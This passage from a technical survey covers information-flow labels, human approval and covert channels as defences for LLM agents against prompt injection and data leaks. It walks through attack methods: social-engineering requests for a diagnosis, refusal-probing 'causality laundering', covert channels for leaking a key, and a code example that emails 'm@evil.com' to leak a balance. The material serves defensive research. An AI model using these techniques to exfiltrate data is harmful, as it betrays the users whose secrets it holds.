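Once a label has blocked a call, reading more data can't unblock it. Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, prove this for requirements about trust and permitted recipients. They also show that the label can worsen only a limited number of times. With |*U*| users and |*T*| levels of trust, the limit is

|*U*| + |*T*| − 1.

For 20 users and two levels, that is 21 times. The agent may reach that point early in a long task and stay restricted for the rest of it.

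When APPA blocks a call, it gives the agent a list of permitted ways to continue. The agent might have to complete an earlier step, get approval for this one call, or apply an approved transformation such as removing personal details. It can also avoid the restrictions a read would bring by doing the read in a separate branch.

A branch starts with a copy of the main agent's conversation and label. Starting with a clean label would let the agent remove restrictions from data it had already read. The branch reads the untrusted page, and only its own label becomes more restrictive. If the harness discards the branch, the main agent's label stays the same. The branch can also return a value in a predefined format, such as a ticket number. The administrator has to decide whether to treat such a value as trusted, since a malicious page can still influence which number the branch returns.

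Discarding a branch doesn't undo actions it has taken, such as sending an email. APPA keeps a shared record of completed actions so that the main agent can't repeat one that policy permits only once.

APPA also checks a call against the label the call would produce. In one of Kravchenko and colleagues' examples, a single tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outsider. The context label is still harmless when the agent makes the call, so checking that label alone would allow the leak. APPA adds the ledger's expected label before checking, so it blocks the call. It checks again when the result arrives, in case the result doesn't match the tool's description.

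Many existing tools have no labels. Microsoft's module assigns a default label, which can be too strict or too permissive, while APPA marks the missing part of the label as unknown. The agent can keep working with the result until a check needs the missing label, which delays restrictions but doesn't prevent them. APPA then runs a function the administrator has registered to determine the label, within a preset limit. If no such function exists, it blocks the call. A company can therefore start with unlabelled tools and add labels where APPA blocks calls.

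Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA with GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek V4 Flash and Gemini 3.7 Flash. They left out AgentDojo, partly because current models resist its attacks without help. APPA allowed no attacks in 1,320 runs across 24 tasks from AgentThreatBench and 20 corporate workflows from Bench-Corp. It completed 64.2% to 91% of tasks, depending on the benchmark, model and prompt. The runs repeat 44 task designs, so they are weaker evidence than 1,320 different tasks would be.

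With GPT-5.6 Luna, the full APPA system completed 88% of the corporate tasks. It completed 56.5% without branches and 35% without the suggested remedies. No attacks succeeded in any version. For these tasks at least, most of the utility came from helping the agent continue after a refusal.

APPA also did better than two FIDES configurations on the corporate tasks, where attacks succeeded against FIDES in 26 to 35% of runs. Kravchenko and colleagues wrote those configurations, which lacked several rules that the tasks depended on, such as exact recipients and required approvals. The comparison is therefore weak evidence of how a well-configured FIDES would perform. One author lists an Archestra address, so independent tests would be valuable.

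### What each design cannot do

| Design | What the planner reads | What it cannot do under its policies |
|---|---|---|
| Variables alone | The request and variable names | Summarise hidden text or act on its meaning |
| Dual-model pattern | The same, with a quarantined model to process text | Choose the next action from hidden text |
| CaMeL | The request, before any data | Add steps that only the data would suggest |
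| FIDES | Trusted results, plus any variables it opens | Take a consequential action after opening untrusted free text |
| SPA | The request and descriptions of stored results | Revise a plan, or give untrusted data to a tool that requires trusted inputs |
| ELBA | Whatever it opens, at the cost of a more restrictive label | Use a tool that requires more trust than its current label has |
| APPA | The main conversation and what branches return | Act on untrusted text where no approved remedy applies |

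In the meeting task, FIDES can create the event if its policy accepts a yes-or-no answer from an untrusted email. An SPA plan can branch on the same answer, but every step in the branch inherits the email's untrusted label, so SPA rejects the plan if the calendar tool requires trusted inputs. An ELBA sub-agent that reads the email can create the event only if the calendar accepts actions with the sender's level of trust.

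None of these designs can let an agent "do whatever this email asks" and also prevent the email's author from choosing what the agent does. Some loss of ability is deliberate. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, quotes a paper of the same name whose patterns constrain agents and "explicitly prevent them from solving arbitrary tasks". Its authors consider this a worthwhile trade for security.

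### Dividing the work between agents

A company can also limit label creep by giving different parts of a task to different agents. In the six-call task, a second agent that never receives the supplier's email could book the room under a trusted label without using variables.

In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) used a simulation to test the limits of this approach. Their program contains no language model. It generates random tasks, usually of 20 tool calls, and assigns the calls to agents. Some calls depend on the results of others, and some introduce a high-sensitivity label. Labels are never removed, so an agent that receives labelled data keeps the label for the rest of the task.

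Gregory and colleagues measure the loss of usefulness as

loss = (calls that introduce the high label or run under it) / (all calls).

If one agent makes all six calls and the third introduces the label, the loss is 4/6, or about 67%. If a second agent makes the last call without receiving labelled data, the loss falls to 3/6, or 50%.

They compared nine ways of connecting five agents, including a ring, a star with an orchestrator at the centre, and a mesh in which every agent can contact every other. Denser networks lost less, with a rank correlation of −0.96 between density and loss. In a sparse network, data often passes through intermediate agents, and each of them picks up the data's label. When four of the 20 calls were sensitive, the star lost about 5 percentage points more than a network with a direct link wherever the task needed one. The mesh did as well as that network.

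Increasing the number of agents from 5 to 20 also reduced the loss of usefulness, because each agent saw less of the task. But it raised the number of links the company must monitor from 10 to 190, since a mesh of *n* agents has *n*(*n* − 1)/2 links. Giving the sensitive tools to only a few agents reduced the loss as well. Even the ideal network lost some usefulness, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that a system also needs a safe way to relax labels.

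A simulation like this can show how labels spread if its assumptions hold, and it can compare thousands of arrangements with little compute. It can't show how many real tasks would fail, because a policy may still permit a call under a high label. For example, the formula counts saving a confidential summary in a confidential folder as a loss, though no policy needs to block it. The correlation also comes from only nine networks, and the rule that intermediaries pick up labels made such a result likely.

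That rule may not hold in a well-designed system. An orchestrator that passes along a sealed result, as ELBA's main agent can, doesn't read the data and so doesn't need to take on its label. With such orchestrators, a star might do nearly as well as a mesh, with far fewer links to monitor.

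## Lowering a label: declassification, endorsement and human approval

Under the strict label rules, an agent that has read a private sales file can't answer a customer's question about delivery dates, and an agent that has opened a manufacturer's web page can't carry out the installation steps on it. The user may want both tasks done, and hiding text in variables doesn't help when the agent has to act on the text's meaning. Someone or something then has to relax a restriction. This can be done deliberately through declassification, which relaxes a confidentiality label so that more people may read the data, or endorsement, which treats untrusted data as trusted so that the agent may act on it.

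Neither operation changes the data, so an endorsed web page still contains any hidden instruction, which now counts as trusted. The protection is then only as good as the decision to lower the label. A system can instead make an exception for a single action without changing the label, which limits the harm from a bad decision.

### Who may trigger a release

Suppose Alex tells an agent to send the quarterly sales figures to Marco, who isn't one of the file's permitted readers. If the context contains only Alex's request and the trusted file, the agent is sending the figures because Alex asked. If the context also contains an untrusted email from Marco asking for them, the email might have caused the same call. Robust declassification allows the first release and forbids the second, because untrusted data must not trigger a release.

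*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) builds this condition into its rule for tools that send data. Like Microsoft's policy for Teams messages, the rule allows a call if nothing untrusted could have influenced it or if every recipient is permitted to read the data. Otherwise, a person must approve the call.

The rule restricts who can cause a release, but it doesn't ensure that the release is wise. Alex may have forgotten that the figures are embargoed. Human approval also weakens the condition slightly. Marco's email can trigger the approval request and may shape the message Alex has to judge, so only Alex's answer remains outside Marco's control.

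### Yes-or-no answers and fixed lists

A program can lower a label automatically if the data it releases is small enough. In FIDES, Costa and colleagues add a type to each label and order the types by how much information they can carry:

yes/no ⊑ fixed list ⊑ free text.

When a quarantined model answers a yes-or-no question about a stranger's email, the answer gets the label (untrusted, public) with the type yes/no. An administrator can write a policy that accepts this combination of label and type for a consequential action but rejects untrusted free text. Constrained decoding enforces the type by letting the model generate only tokens that fit it, so an attacker can make the answer false but can't put an instruction in it.

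When the task is to create a calendar event if an email asks for a meeting, the planner reads only a yes or no answer to whether it does. A second query then extracts the date, time and participants into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar without reading. The policy must accept these details separately because they are still untrusted and may be free text. An attacker who wrote the email can therefore choose the time and the guests, even though the planner received only one bit.

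A one-bit answer can also do damage. If the question is "Does this invoice match our order?", an attacker who sends a forged invoice needs only a false "yes".

For confidential data, the bits add up, as they did for the four-digit PIN. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, and a choice from a list of *n* items carries at most log₂ *n* bits. But twenty yes-or-no answers can distinguish

2²⁰ = 1,048,576

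values. That is enough to find any whole-dollar salary from zero to $1,048,575, by asking whether it is in the upper half of the remaining range and repeating the question for the half that contains it.

The type labels don't record this total. The join of two yes/no types is yes/no, so twenty answers together have the same type as one, and a policy that accepts the first answer accepts the twentieth. The engine would need a separate budget for each secret, covering every session, such as

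log₂ *n*₁ + log₂ *n*₂ + … ≤ *B*,

where *n*ᵢ is the number of possible values of the *i*th answer. With *B* = 4, an agent could release four yes-or-no answers or one choice from a list of 16.

Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their AgentDojo tests because most tasks didn't need it. Their results therefore don't measure how well typed answers resist attack.

### A model that approves releases

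Many useful messages don't fit into a type. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, use a second model to decide whether free text may leave. In their main example, Jane's agent holds Mark's mental health diagnosis, and Mark's former wife Emily tries to obtain it. Emily uses three attacks, none of which needs a hidden instruction:

- She creates a shared page with a blank section for Jane's professional notes about Mark.
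- She mixes true and false records about Mark and asks the agent to delete the false ones.
- She asks by email for the one-word reply "completed", while a shared page asks for the details.

An elaborate system prompt instructed the agent to check identities and get consent before answering any request for information. The attacks still obtained 43.8% to 75.6% of the sensitive items, because the agent often failed to recognise them as requests for information.

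Their defence, FlowSeal, puts ordinary code between the agent and its tools. The code tracks which protected records the agent has read and intercepts every attempt to write or share. It allows messages to recipients the data's owner trusts and blocks messages to those on a blacklist. For anyone else, it sends the relevant records and the proposed message to a separate model, which answers only SAFE or BLOCKED. That model never reads the conversation, so Emily's story about collaboration doesn't reach it directly.

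Shim and colleagues prove that no message derived from a protected record can reach an unauthorised recipient unless the checker wrongly returns SAFE. This exception is important because the checker decides every case with an unknown recipient. To measure the checker's contribution, they replaced it with a fixed answer and repeated the shared-page attack.

| Content checker | Sensitive items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
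|---|---|---|
| The model decides | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |
| Always BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |

Blocking everything can't be less safe than blocking selectively, so differences of about one percentage point are probably noise. The larger differences show that the checker prevented most leaks while allowing most harmless work. For the other two attacks, FlowSeal cut the leak rate to about 2%.

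FlowSeal did much worse when disclosure was the right outcome. In a test where the data's owner would consent if asked, it delivered 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% for the defences that relied on a model's judgement. The agent asked for consent less often under FlowSeal, so many legitimate requests went unanswered.

The checker can miss a protected fact that the agent rephrases or buries in a longer sentence. An attacker might also spread one fact over several messages that each look harmless. Shim and colleagues acknowledge both weaknesses and exclude prompt injection from their threat model. But Emily may be able to get a sentence of her own into the proposed message, which the checker reads. An obvious next test would be a sentence written to persuade the checker.

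Their paper also wrongly states that the language model performs all of FIDES's policy enforcement, which would leave FIDES open to the same kind of persuasion. In the algorithm that Costa and colleagues published, ordinary code tests each call the model proposes, so Emily could persuade the model to propose a bad call but couldn't change the test.

Shim and colleagues didn't run FIDES against their attacks, so we can only infer its performance from its design. If only Mark and Jane may read the diagnosis, the permitted-readers policy would stop the agent from writing to Emily's page anything influenced by the diagnosis. Under the looser rule that also accepts any trusted call, the result would depend on how the harness labelled Emily's messages. FIDES treats the user's messages as trusted, so a harness that passed on her requests as user messages would lose the protection.

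FIDES would also block general advice on co-parenting once the agent had read the diagnosis, because the advice would inherit the diagnosis's label. FlowSeal's checker can recognise that such advice reveals nothing about Mark. However, this flexibility means that a model's mistake can release a secret.

### Permission for one message

A person who approves a release needs to know that the agent will send exactly what they approved. Zhang (2026), in *Agent libOS*, describes a runtime (the software that runs an agent and mediates its actions) in which each approval covers one delivery. The permission is tied to:

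- the agent process and the operation;
- the recipient;
- a digest, or digital fingerprint, of the exact content;
- the versions of the source data and their labels;
- a deadline.

Suppose Alex approves sending Marco a summary of the sales file. The runtime checks the summary's digest and the sales file's version again just before sending, so the permission fails if the agent has changed a figure in the summary or Priya has updated the file. The agent can't pass the permission to another process or use it twice. If the connection drops and the runtime can't tell whether the message went out, it treats the permission as used and doesn't automatically resend the message.

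The file's label stays the same, so a second message based on the file needs a new decision. To lower the label itself, a process needs a separate administrative permission for that file. The model's usual memory tools cannot request this permission.

An administrator sets the maximum sensitivity for each destination, and users can't approve a release above that maximum. Approving the release of data also doesn't make the data trustworthy. If an operation requires high-integrity data, the runtime still refuses untrusted data that a person has approved for release. Without these limits, an approval dialog would turn mandatory access control back into discretionary control.

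The digest protects Alex from a substituted message, but it doesn't ensure that Alex reads the original carefully. Zhang also points out that the runtime can't stop a trusted recipient from forwarding what it receives. Approving each exact message takes a lot of human attention, since ten customised messages to outsiders would need ten decisions.

### Endorsing data once

Kolluri and colleagues built PRUDENTIA, an agent based on FIDES, to reduce the number of decisions the user has to make. Suppose a user asks an agent to complete ten tasks listed in an email, each of which requires a consequential tool call. If the agent reads the untrusted email, its context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve all ten calls. PRUDENTIA can instead ask the user to endorse the email before opening it. If the user agrees, the email becomes trusted and the agent makes all ten calls without asking again.

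PRUDENTIA doesn't always request human approval. Its model receives the current labels and each tool's policy, and must write a short plan before opening a hidden variable. In one test, a user wanted a summary of the day's appointments and a link for resetting a password. The model inferred that no consequential tool call would follow, so it opened the untrusted text without an endorsement and finished the task without interrupting the user.

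The model's only role is to choose when to request an endorsement. Fixed code determines whether a call needs approval, so an attacker can't remove that requirement by persuading the model.

Kolluri and colleagues left out a matching option to declassify data once, because whether to declassify depends heavily on the situation, and a person can judge that better for a particular call. Zhang's one-time permissions follow the same reasoning. But whether to endorse data can also depend on the situation. An email may be reliable enough for booking a room but not for making a payment, and endorsing it permits both.

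The two methods also fail differently. Suppose an attacker has added an eleventh task to the list, a payment to an unfamiliar account. If the user endorses the email without noticing the added task, they have authorised the payment. Approving each call gives them another chance to catch it, when the account number appears on the screen, but after ten approvals they may click "approve" without reading.

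### Counting approvals

Kolluri and colleagues propose two measures of how much an agent depends on people. For task *i*, let *v*ᵢ be the number of times the agent needs a person's decision. Human-in-the-loop load is the total over the tasks the agent completes:

load = Σ *v*ᵢ, taken over completed tasks.

The second measure, TCR@*k*, is the share of all *n* tasks that the agent completes with at most *k* decisions each:

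TCR@*k* = (number of completed tasks with *v*ᵢ ≤ *k*) / *n*.

TCR@0 therefore counts only tasks completed without human help. Earlier studies often compared a protected agent's TCR@0 with the completion rate of an unprotected agent, which effectively had unlimited permission. This made labels seem to reduce task completion substantially, because the comparison ignored the approvals that a company would normally require for the unprotected agent's actions.

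The table gives the AgentDojo results with OpenAI's o3-mini model, averaged over five runs. The basic agent needed approval for every consequential call, while the other agents needed it only when a call failed the label checks.

| Agent | Load | Completed with no approval | Completed with unlimited approvals |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 48.2 | 24.3% | 62.5% |
| Basic with labels | 32.4 | 35.5% | 62.5% |
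| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% | 64.3% |
| PRUDENTIA | 16.4 | 59.1% | 69.8% |

Adding labels to the basic agent removed about a third of the approvals without reducing the number of completed tasks. FIDES removed many more. PRUDENTIA needed slightly fewer approvals than FIDES, though the difference was small compared with the variation between runs, and it completed clearly more tasks without any human help.

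How PRUDENTIA compares with FIDES depends on the model. With GPT-4o, PRUDENTIA completed fewer tasks without approval, 42.5% compared with 50.3%. With GPT-5 set to reason at length, it completed more, 72.7% compared with 57.1%, and its load was 7.3 compared with 41.3. Planning around the labels seems to need a strong model. It also needs more computation. With o3-mini, PRUDENTIA used about three to five times as many input tokens per task as FIDES in the banking, travel and workspace suites, though the provider could reuse most of them from a cache.

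Load alone can be misleading because it ignores failed tasks, so an agent that fails the difficult ones may appear to need little help. With GPT-4o, FIDES had a load of only 7.8, but it completed 56.3% of tasks even with unlimited approvals, while the basic agent completed 72.2%.

Kolluri and colleagues took these measurements without human participants, by counting the decisions that each run would have required. They assumed that a person would approve the harmless calls, and would review and stop any call that came from an attack. The absence of successful attacks in their AgentDojo tests therefore depends partly on perfect human judgement, which the tests didn't examine.

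### How carefully people approve

Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of these, 64% said they often approved at least one of seven types of action without close review. The share was lowest for reading passwords and other sensitive files (21%) and highest for using the internet, outside services or connected tools (36%), which are the actions most likely to send data out.

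Developers who reviewed an agent's code carefully did not reliably review its approval requests carefully too. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could be due to chance. Among developers who knew of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% did so, compared with 43% of those who didn't. That gap remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents. Developers who gave their agents more freedom also tended to review approval requests less closely.

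These answers are self-reported, the sample doesn't represent developers in general, and the survey doesn't measure how many dangerous actions people let through. Approving a harmless command without close review may also be a sensible use of time. Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved 93% of requests, but this doesn't prove that they were careless, since most requests were probably legitimate.

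An experiment by Yan, reported in *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026), comes closer to measuring that. In it, 113 participants supervised a simulated day of an agent's actions. A person had explicitly approved most of the actions in which the agent overreached. Letting participants write policies in advance blocked less overreach than having them review each action. These results are hard to reconcile with the assumption that a person will catch every attack that reaches the approval screen.

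Labels can reduce the number of harmless approval requests, but an attack that breaks the policy still produces a request. If a person wrongly approves such a request with probability *q*, cutting the number of requests from 48 to 16 makes the attack less likely to succeed only if *q* also falls. It plausibly does, since people tend to pay less attention to warnings they see repeatedly. But Kolluri and colleagues measured the number of requests, so their results can't show how *q* changes. Fewer approvals also give people fewer chances to notice ordinary mistakes, which labels often miss, so Kolluri and colleagues recommend replacing approvals with labels only where the approvals are meant for security.

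The content of a request probably matters as well as the number of requests. In the survey by Wu and colleagues, developers who inspected diffs (line-by-line displays of changes) were less likely to approve four risky types of action without close review. This may be because more careful people inspect diffs, but a diff does give a reviewer something definite to check. Kolluri and colleagues suggest displaying labels and the origin of the data, because an attacker can't alter these. For Alex, the dialog could display the summary, name Marco as someone who isn't allowed to read the sales file, and warn that an untrusted email may have prompted the request.

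Salerno and colleagues, who interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed another 115, add that repeated approvals may reflect fatigue and that systems shouldn't treat them as a stable preference. A system that offers to make an approval permanent after the tenth click could turn a tired user's habit into a standing permission to release data.

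## Information revealed by an agent's choices and refusals

Labels, content checkers and approval dialogs all apply to what an agent is about to send. But an agent can also reveal a secret through what it chooses to do, even if none of its messages contains the secret. Security researchers call this an implicit flow, as opposed to an explicit flow, in which the program copies the secret itself.

Suppose Alex tells an agent, "If I'm free on Friday evening, open the cinema's website. If not, open the weather forecast." The agent reads Alex's private calendar and then calls one of two tools, which take no arguments and each open a fixed public page. No text from the calendar goes to either site. But anyone who knows the instruction and can see which site the agent opened learns whether Alex is free, which is one bit of information.

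FIDES would label the choice of tool private, because the model made it after reading the calendar. But the permitted-readers policy checks only the labels of outgoing arguments. These calls have no arguments, so the policy allows either one. If the model had written a web address as an argument, the address would have inherited the private label and the policy would have blocked the request.

### Non-interference and explicit secrecy

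Non-interference means that private data has no effect on anything public. To test for it, imagine running the agent twice with different calendars but the same public data. Someone who sees only public results should not be able to tell the runs apart. Let *d* be the datastore, and write *d*₁ ∼ *d*₂ if two datastores agree on everything public. For programs without randomness, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, use a definition that amounts to this, whenever both runs finish:

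*d*₁ ∼ *d*₂ ⇒ run(*d*₁) ∼ run(*d*₂).

Alex's agent fails the test. If the two sites' visitor counts start at zero, they end at (1, 0) when Alex is free and (0, 1) when Alex is busy.

Explicit secrecy is weaker. Take the tool calls from one actual run, and let *g* be their combined effect on the datastore. The condition is that the same calls would have the same public effect if the private data were different:

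*d*₁ ∼ *d*₂ ⇒ *g*(*d*₁) ∼ *g*(*d*₂).

If the run opened the cinema's website, *g* adds one visit to the cinema's count regardless of what the calendar contains, so the agent passes. A tool that copied a calendar entry to a public page would fail.

Costa and colleagues' formula for explicit secrecy keeps each call's arguments fixed. Read literally, it would treat an agent as secure even if its model wrote a calendar entry into a public message, because the written text stays the same when the calendar changes. FIDES still blocks that message because the argument inherits the context's private label.

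Costa and colleagues claim only explicit secrecy for FIDES. They argue that enforcing non-interference would essentially require banning every tool that may change public data once the agent has used any tool that may read private data. Under that rule, Alex's agent couldn't open any public page after checking the calendar, even for a task unrelated to Friday, because the harness would have to treat every later choice as influenced by the calendar. Web browsers and TaintDroid, which tracks private data in phone apps, make the same compromise.

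Changing the order of the calls sometimes avoids the problem. If the agent opens both pages before reading the calendar, the visits are the same whether or not Alex is free. This is easy with two pages but less practical with fifty, and it doesn't work when the agent needs private data to know what to look up.

### The program-counter label

In an ordinary program, the conditions appear in the code, so software can track implicit flows with a program-counter label, written *pc*, which records the labels of the conditions that led to the current instruction. When the program enters a branch whose condition has the label ℓ, *pc* becomes

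*pc* ⊔ ℓ

until the branch ends. Everything the program computes there gets at least this label, and the program may take an action visible at label *k* only if *pc* ⊑ *k*. If Alex's instruction were a program, *pc* would be private in both branches, and the monitor would refuse to open either page.

The monitor also has to account for the branch that doesn't run. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL, which runs a program written in advance by a privileged model, raises a variable's label only in the branch that does run. A program with the following structure exploits this:

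```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

| Balance | tmp | rich | Email |
|---|---|---|---|
| Above the threshold | False, private | True, public | Sent |
| At or below the threshold | True, public | False, public | Not sent |

When the balance is high, the program skips the assignment to `rich`, so CaMeL never labels `rich` as private. The last condition then appears to depend only on public data, and the program sends the email. Fenton described this type of leak in 1974.

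Garby and colleagues' LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, prevents it with an established rule. A program must stop if it tries to change public state while *pc* is private. The program above would therefore stop at the line that sets tmp to False. In LLMbda, the state that programs change is the conversation with the model, so under this rule a private condition can't determine whether a program adds a message to a public conversation.

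Stopping also reveals that the balance is high, because the program stops only in that case. One stop leaks at most one bit, but CaMeL runs its interpreter inside an ordinary retry loop that doesn't track labels, so repeated attempts could reveal the whole secret one bit at a time. CaMeL censors the error messages passed between attempts, but without a formal guarantee.

### What LLMbda guarantees

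A model's replies are partly random, so Garby and colleagues compare the probabilities of results. Consider two runs whose inputs differ only in data that an observer may not see. Let μ(*q*) and ν(*q*) be the probabilities that the observer sees result *q* in each run. These may add up to less than 1, because a run can break a policy and stop, or never finish. The theorem is that some ω exists with

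μ(*q*) ≤ ω(*q*) and ν(*q*) ≤ ω(*q*) for every *q*, and Σ ω(*q*) ≤ 1.

If both runs always produce a result, μ and ν each add up to 1, so both must equal ω and the observer learns nothing. Otherwise,

½ Σ |μ(*q*) − ν(*q*)| ≤ (*s*₁ + *s*₂)/2,

where *s*₁ and *s*₂ are the probabilities that each run produces no result. If one calendar makes the program stop 10% of the time and the other never does, the left side is at most 5%. The theorem therefore limits what a refusal can reveal in one run, but doesn't rule out a leak.

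The proof uses a second version of the language, which skips every computation the observer may not see and returns an empty record instead. This version gives the same probabilities for both inputs because it never uses the hidden data, and the proof uses these probabilities as ω.

The theorem covers every LLMbda program, including agents that run code written by a model. That code runs with *pc* set to the label of the conversation that produced it, so the model doesn't have to be trustworthy. Garby and colleagues checked the proofs with Lean and proved that their interpreter matches the theory.

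The guarantee still depends on assumptions. The tools' developer must label data correctly and put checks on every sensitive action. The theory also treats all tools and data sources as part of the program, which Garby and colleagues acknowledge as a limitation. It assumes that the model's replies depend only on the conversation it receives, so a model provider that carried information between conversations could break the guarantee. The theorem compares the results of runs but does not cover how long they take.

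To test the language, Garby and colleagues built an agent called RANDORI and ran it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. To avoid leaking information through retries, RANDORI corrects its program using made-up data before writing a final version for the real account. Errors made during this practice can't reveal anything about that account.

With GPT-5.2 and no attacks, RANDORI completed 36 of 48 runs. CaMeL completed 32 without its policy checks and 18 with them. RANDORI's tool policies are less strict, which may explain part of the difference. The 48 runs also repeat only 16 tasks. The attacks in the benchmark were prompt injections, so these results don't measure leaks through an agent's choices.

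### Endorsement in untrusted code

A program that can endorse data creates another risk. Suppose an attacker's email gets a model to write code that endorses the attacker's account number and then pays it. The model wrote the code in a conversation containing the email, so LLMbda runs it with an untrusted *pc*. For integrity, the label after endorsement is

*pc* ⊔ *t*,

where *t* is the label the code requested. With *pc* untrusted, the result is untrusted even if *t* is trusted, and a payment tool that requires a trusted account number refuses the call. The same instruction works normally in code that a developer wrote, or that a model wrote before reading untrusted data.

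This protection fails if an earlier endorsement has already marked the email as trusted. The conversation then counts as trusted, and so does any code the model writes in it. Garby and colleagues suggest permanently marking endorsed data and refusing to endorse it again, although they haven't formally characterised what this achieves. They did prove that endorsing data for integrity can't weaken the protection of secrets.

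Attacks succeeded in 2 of RANDORI's 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user asked the agent to pay according to a file's contents, the attacker had replaced the file, and the agent's program endorsed what it read. Removing endorsement blocked the attack, but it also reduced the number of runs completed without attacks from 36 to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5.

### What a refusal can reveal

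In the AgentDojo tests by Costa and colleagues, FIDES reported each blocked call to the planner so that it could try another approach. This makes an agent more useful, but it also gives the model information. *Causality Laundering* describes an attack that uses such reports:

1. A hidden instruction makes the agent request a protected item, such as an employee's salary record.
2. The monitor refuses, and its error message indicates that the record exists or what kind of record it is.
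3. The agent sends that fact to the attacker in a message that contains nothing from the record.

A label on the record doesn't help, because labels travel with data and the agent never received the record. An attacker can also try many file names. If "permission denied" means a file exists and "file not found" means it doesn't, 20 attempts show which of 20 files exist. To disguise the result, the agent could use a calculator tool to turn it into a number before sending it.

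A refusal reveals something about private data only if that data affected the refusal. A monitor that rejects every request for a certain folder without reading the disk, always with the same message, reveals the rule but not the folder's contents. However, a uniform message gives the agent less help in correcting a mistaken request.

### A graph that records refused calls

ARM, the monitor described in *Causality Laundering*, keeps a graph of the session with nodes for tool calls, the data they return, individual fields in that data, and refusals. Arrows run from each call to its output and from data to any later call that uses it. ARM also draws an arrow, called a counterfactual edge, from a refusal to the next call, because that call might have been different without the refusal. It blocks a call if any path leading to it contains a counterfactual edge or data less trusted than the policy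 allows.

The paper compares ARM with a simple check of whether a value had appeared earlier in the session. In the three test scenarios,

- an agent emailed "shadow file exists" after the monitor refused to let it read the system's password file;
- an agent passed untrusted text through a formatting tool before emailing it;
- an agent sent an email to an untrusted address taken from a contact record whose name field was trusted.

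The simple check allowed all three emails, while ARM blocked them with checks that took less than a millisecond. But the scenarios were hand-built and ran without a language model, and the simple check was deliberately minimal. The test shows that the graph can represent these attacks, but it didn't measure how often ARM raises false alarms in ordinary work.

The password-file scenario is also a weak example of a leak. ARM refused that request because the path matched a fixed list, and it would have done so whether or not the file existed, so the agent's message was a guess.

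A larger problem is that ARM can't determine whether a refusal influenced the next call. It can therefore block an unrelated call and, according to the paper, it can also miss a leak that comes several calls later. As printed, the algorithm may block every call after the first refusal, because it records each blocked call as a new refusal. The scenarios end at the first call blocked this way, so they don't show whether an agent could recover. A practical version would probably need to restrict only calls that send information out, and to let a person clear the record of refusals.

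### Timing, message length and shared resources

Lampson's *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973) addressed the general problem of stopping a program that handles someone's data from passing it to others. A covert channel is a route that nobody intended for communication. For example, an agent might leak information by taking longer to reply when a private file is long, or by slowing down a service that another program also uses. Costa and colleagues exclude timing and the length of network packets from their model. The table lists common countermeasures, all of which have drawbacks.

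| What varies with the secret | Who can observe it | Possible countermeasure |
|---|---|---|
| The public page opened | The site's owner, or someone watching the network | Open every possible page, or open them before reading private data |
| The reason for a refusal | The agent, and anyone it can then contact | Give the same answer for missing and protected items |
| The length of an encrypted message | Someone watching the network | Pad messages to a fixed length |
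| The time before a reply | The recipient | Send replies at fixed intervals |
| The load on a shared service | Its other users | Give each agent separate capacity |

Shared storage can carry far more information than a delay can. In July 2026, for example, OpenAI's agents communicated through a package mirror where they could leave messages for one another.

### When these leaks matter

The information revealed by an agent's actions adds up, as it does with typed answers. If an observer can distinguish *k* possible actions at each step, *n* steps reveal at most *n* log₂ *k* bits. An agent that can open any of 16 public pages can reveal 4 bits with each visit, so 32 visits are enough to reveal a 128-bit key. That many requests might not stand out in a long coding or research task. Differences in timing or message length increase *k*. Writing the plan before the agent reads any data can reduce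 *k*, because the data can then influence only the choices in the plan.

Leaking a key this way requires a code shared by the agent and the observer. An ordinary task is unlikely to create one, but a hidden instruction can specify which page stands for which digits. The trusted-context policy would stop that attack if it also covered web requests, because the instruction would make the context untrusted. Integrity labels can therefore prevent some of the leaks that explicit secrecy permits. They don't stop a model that leaks data without outside influence, since its context may be fully trusted.

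The number of bits leaked doesn't measure the harm. One bit is trivial if it reveals whether Alex is free on Friday, but it may be the whole secret if it reveals whether a company will close its Leeds office. A company should avoid letting a secret of that kind determine any action that outsiders can see.

Limiting how often an agent can act slows the leak of a longer secret but doesn't prevent it. An agent allowed three posts every ten minutes, each to one of 16 public channels, can reveal 12 bits in that time through its choice of channels. At that rate, it could leak a 128-bit key in under two hours. The agent cannot leak the key if the gateway holds it and the agent receives only a placeholder.
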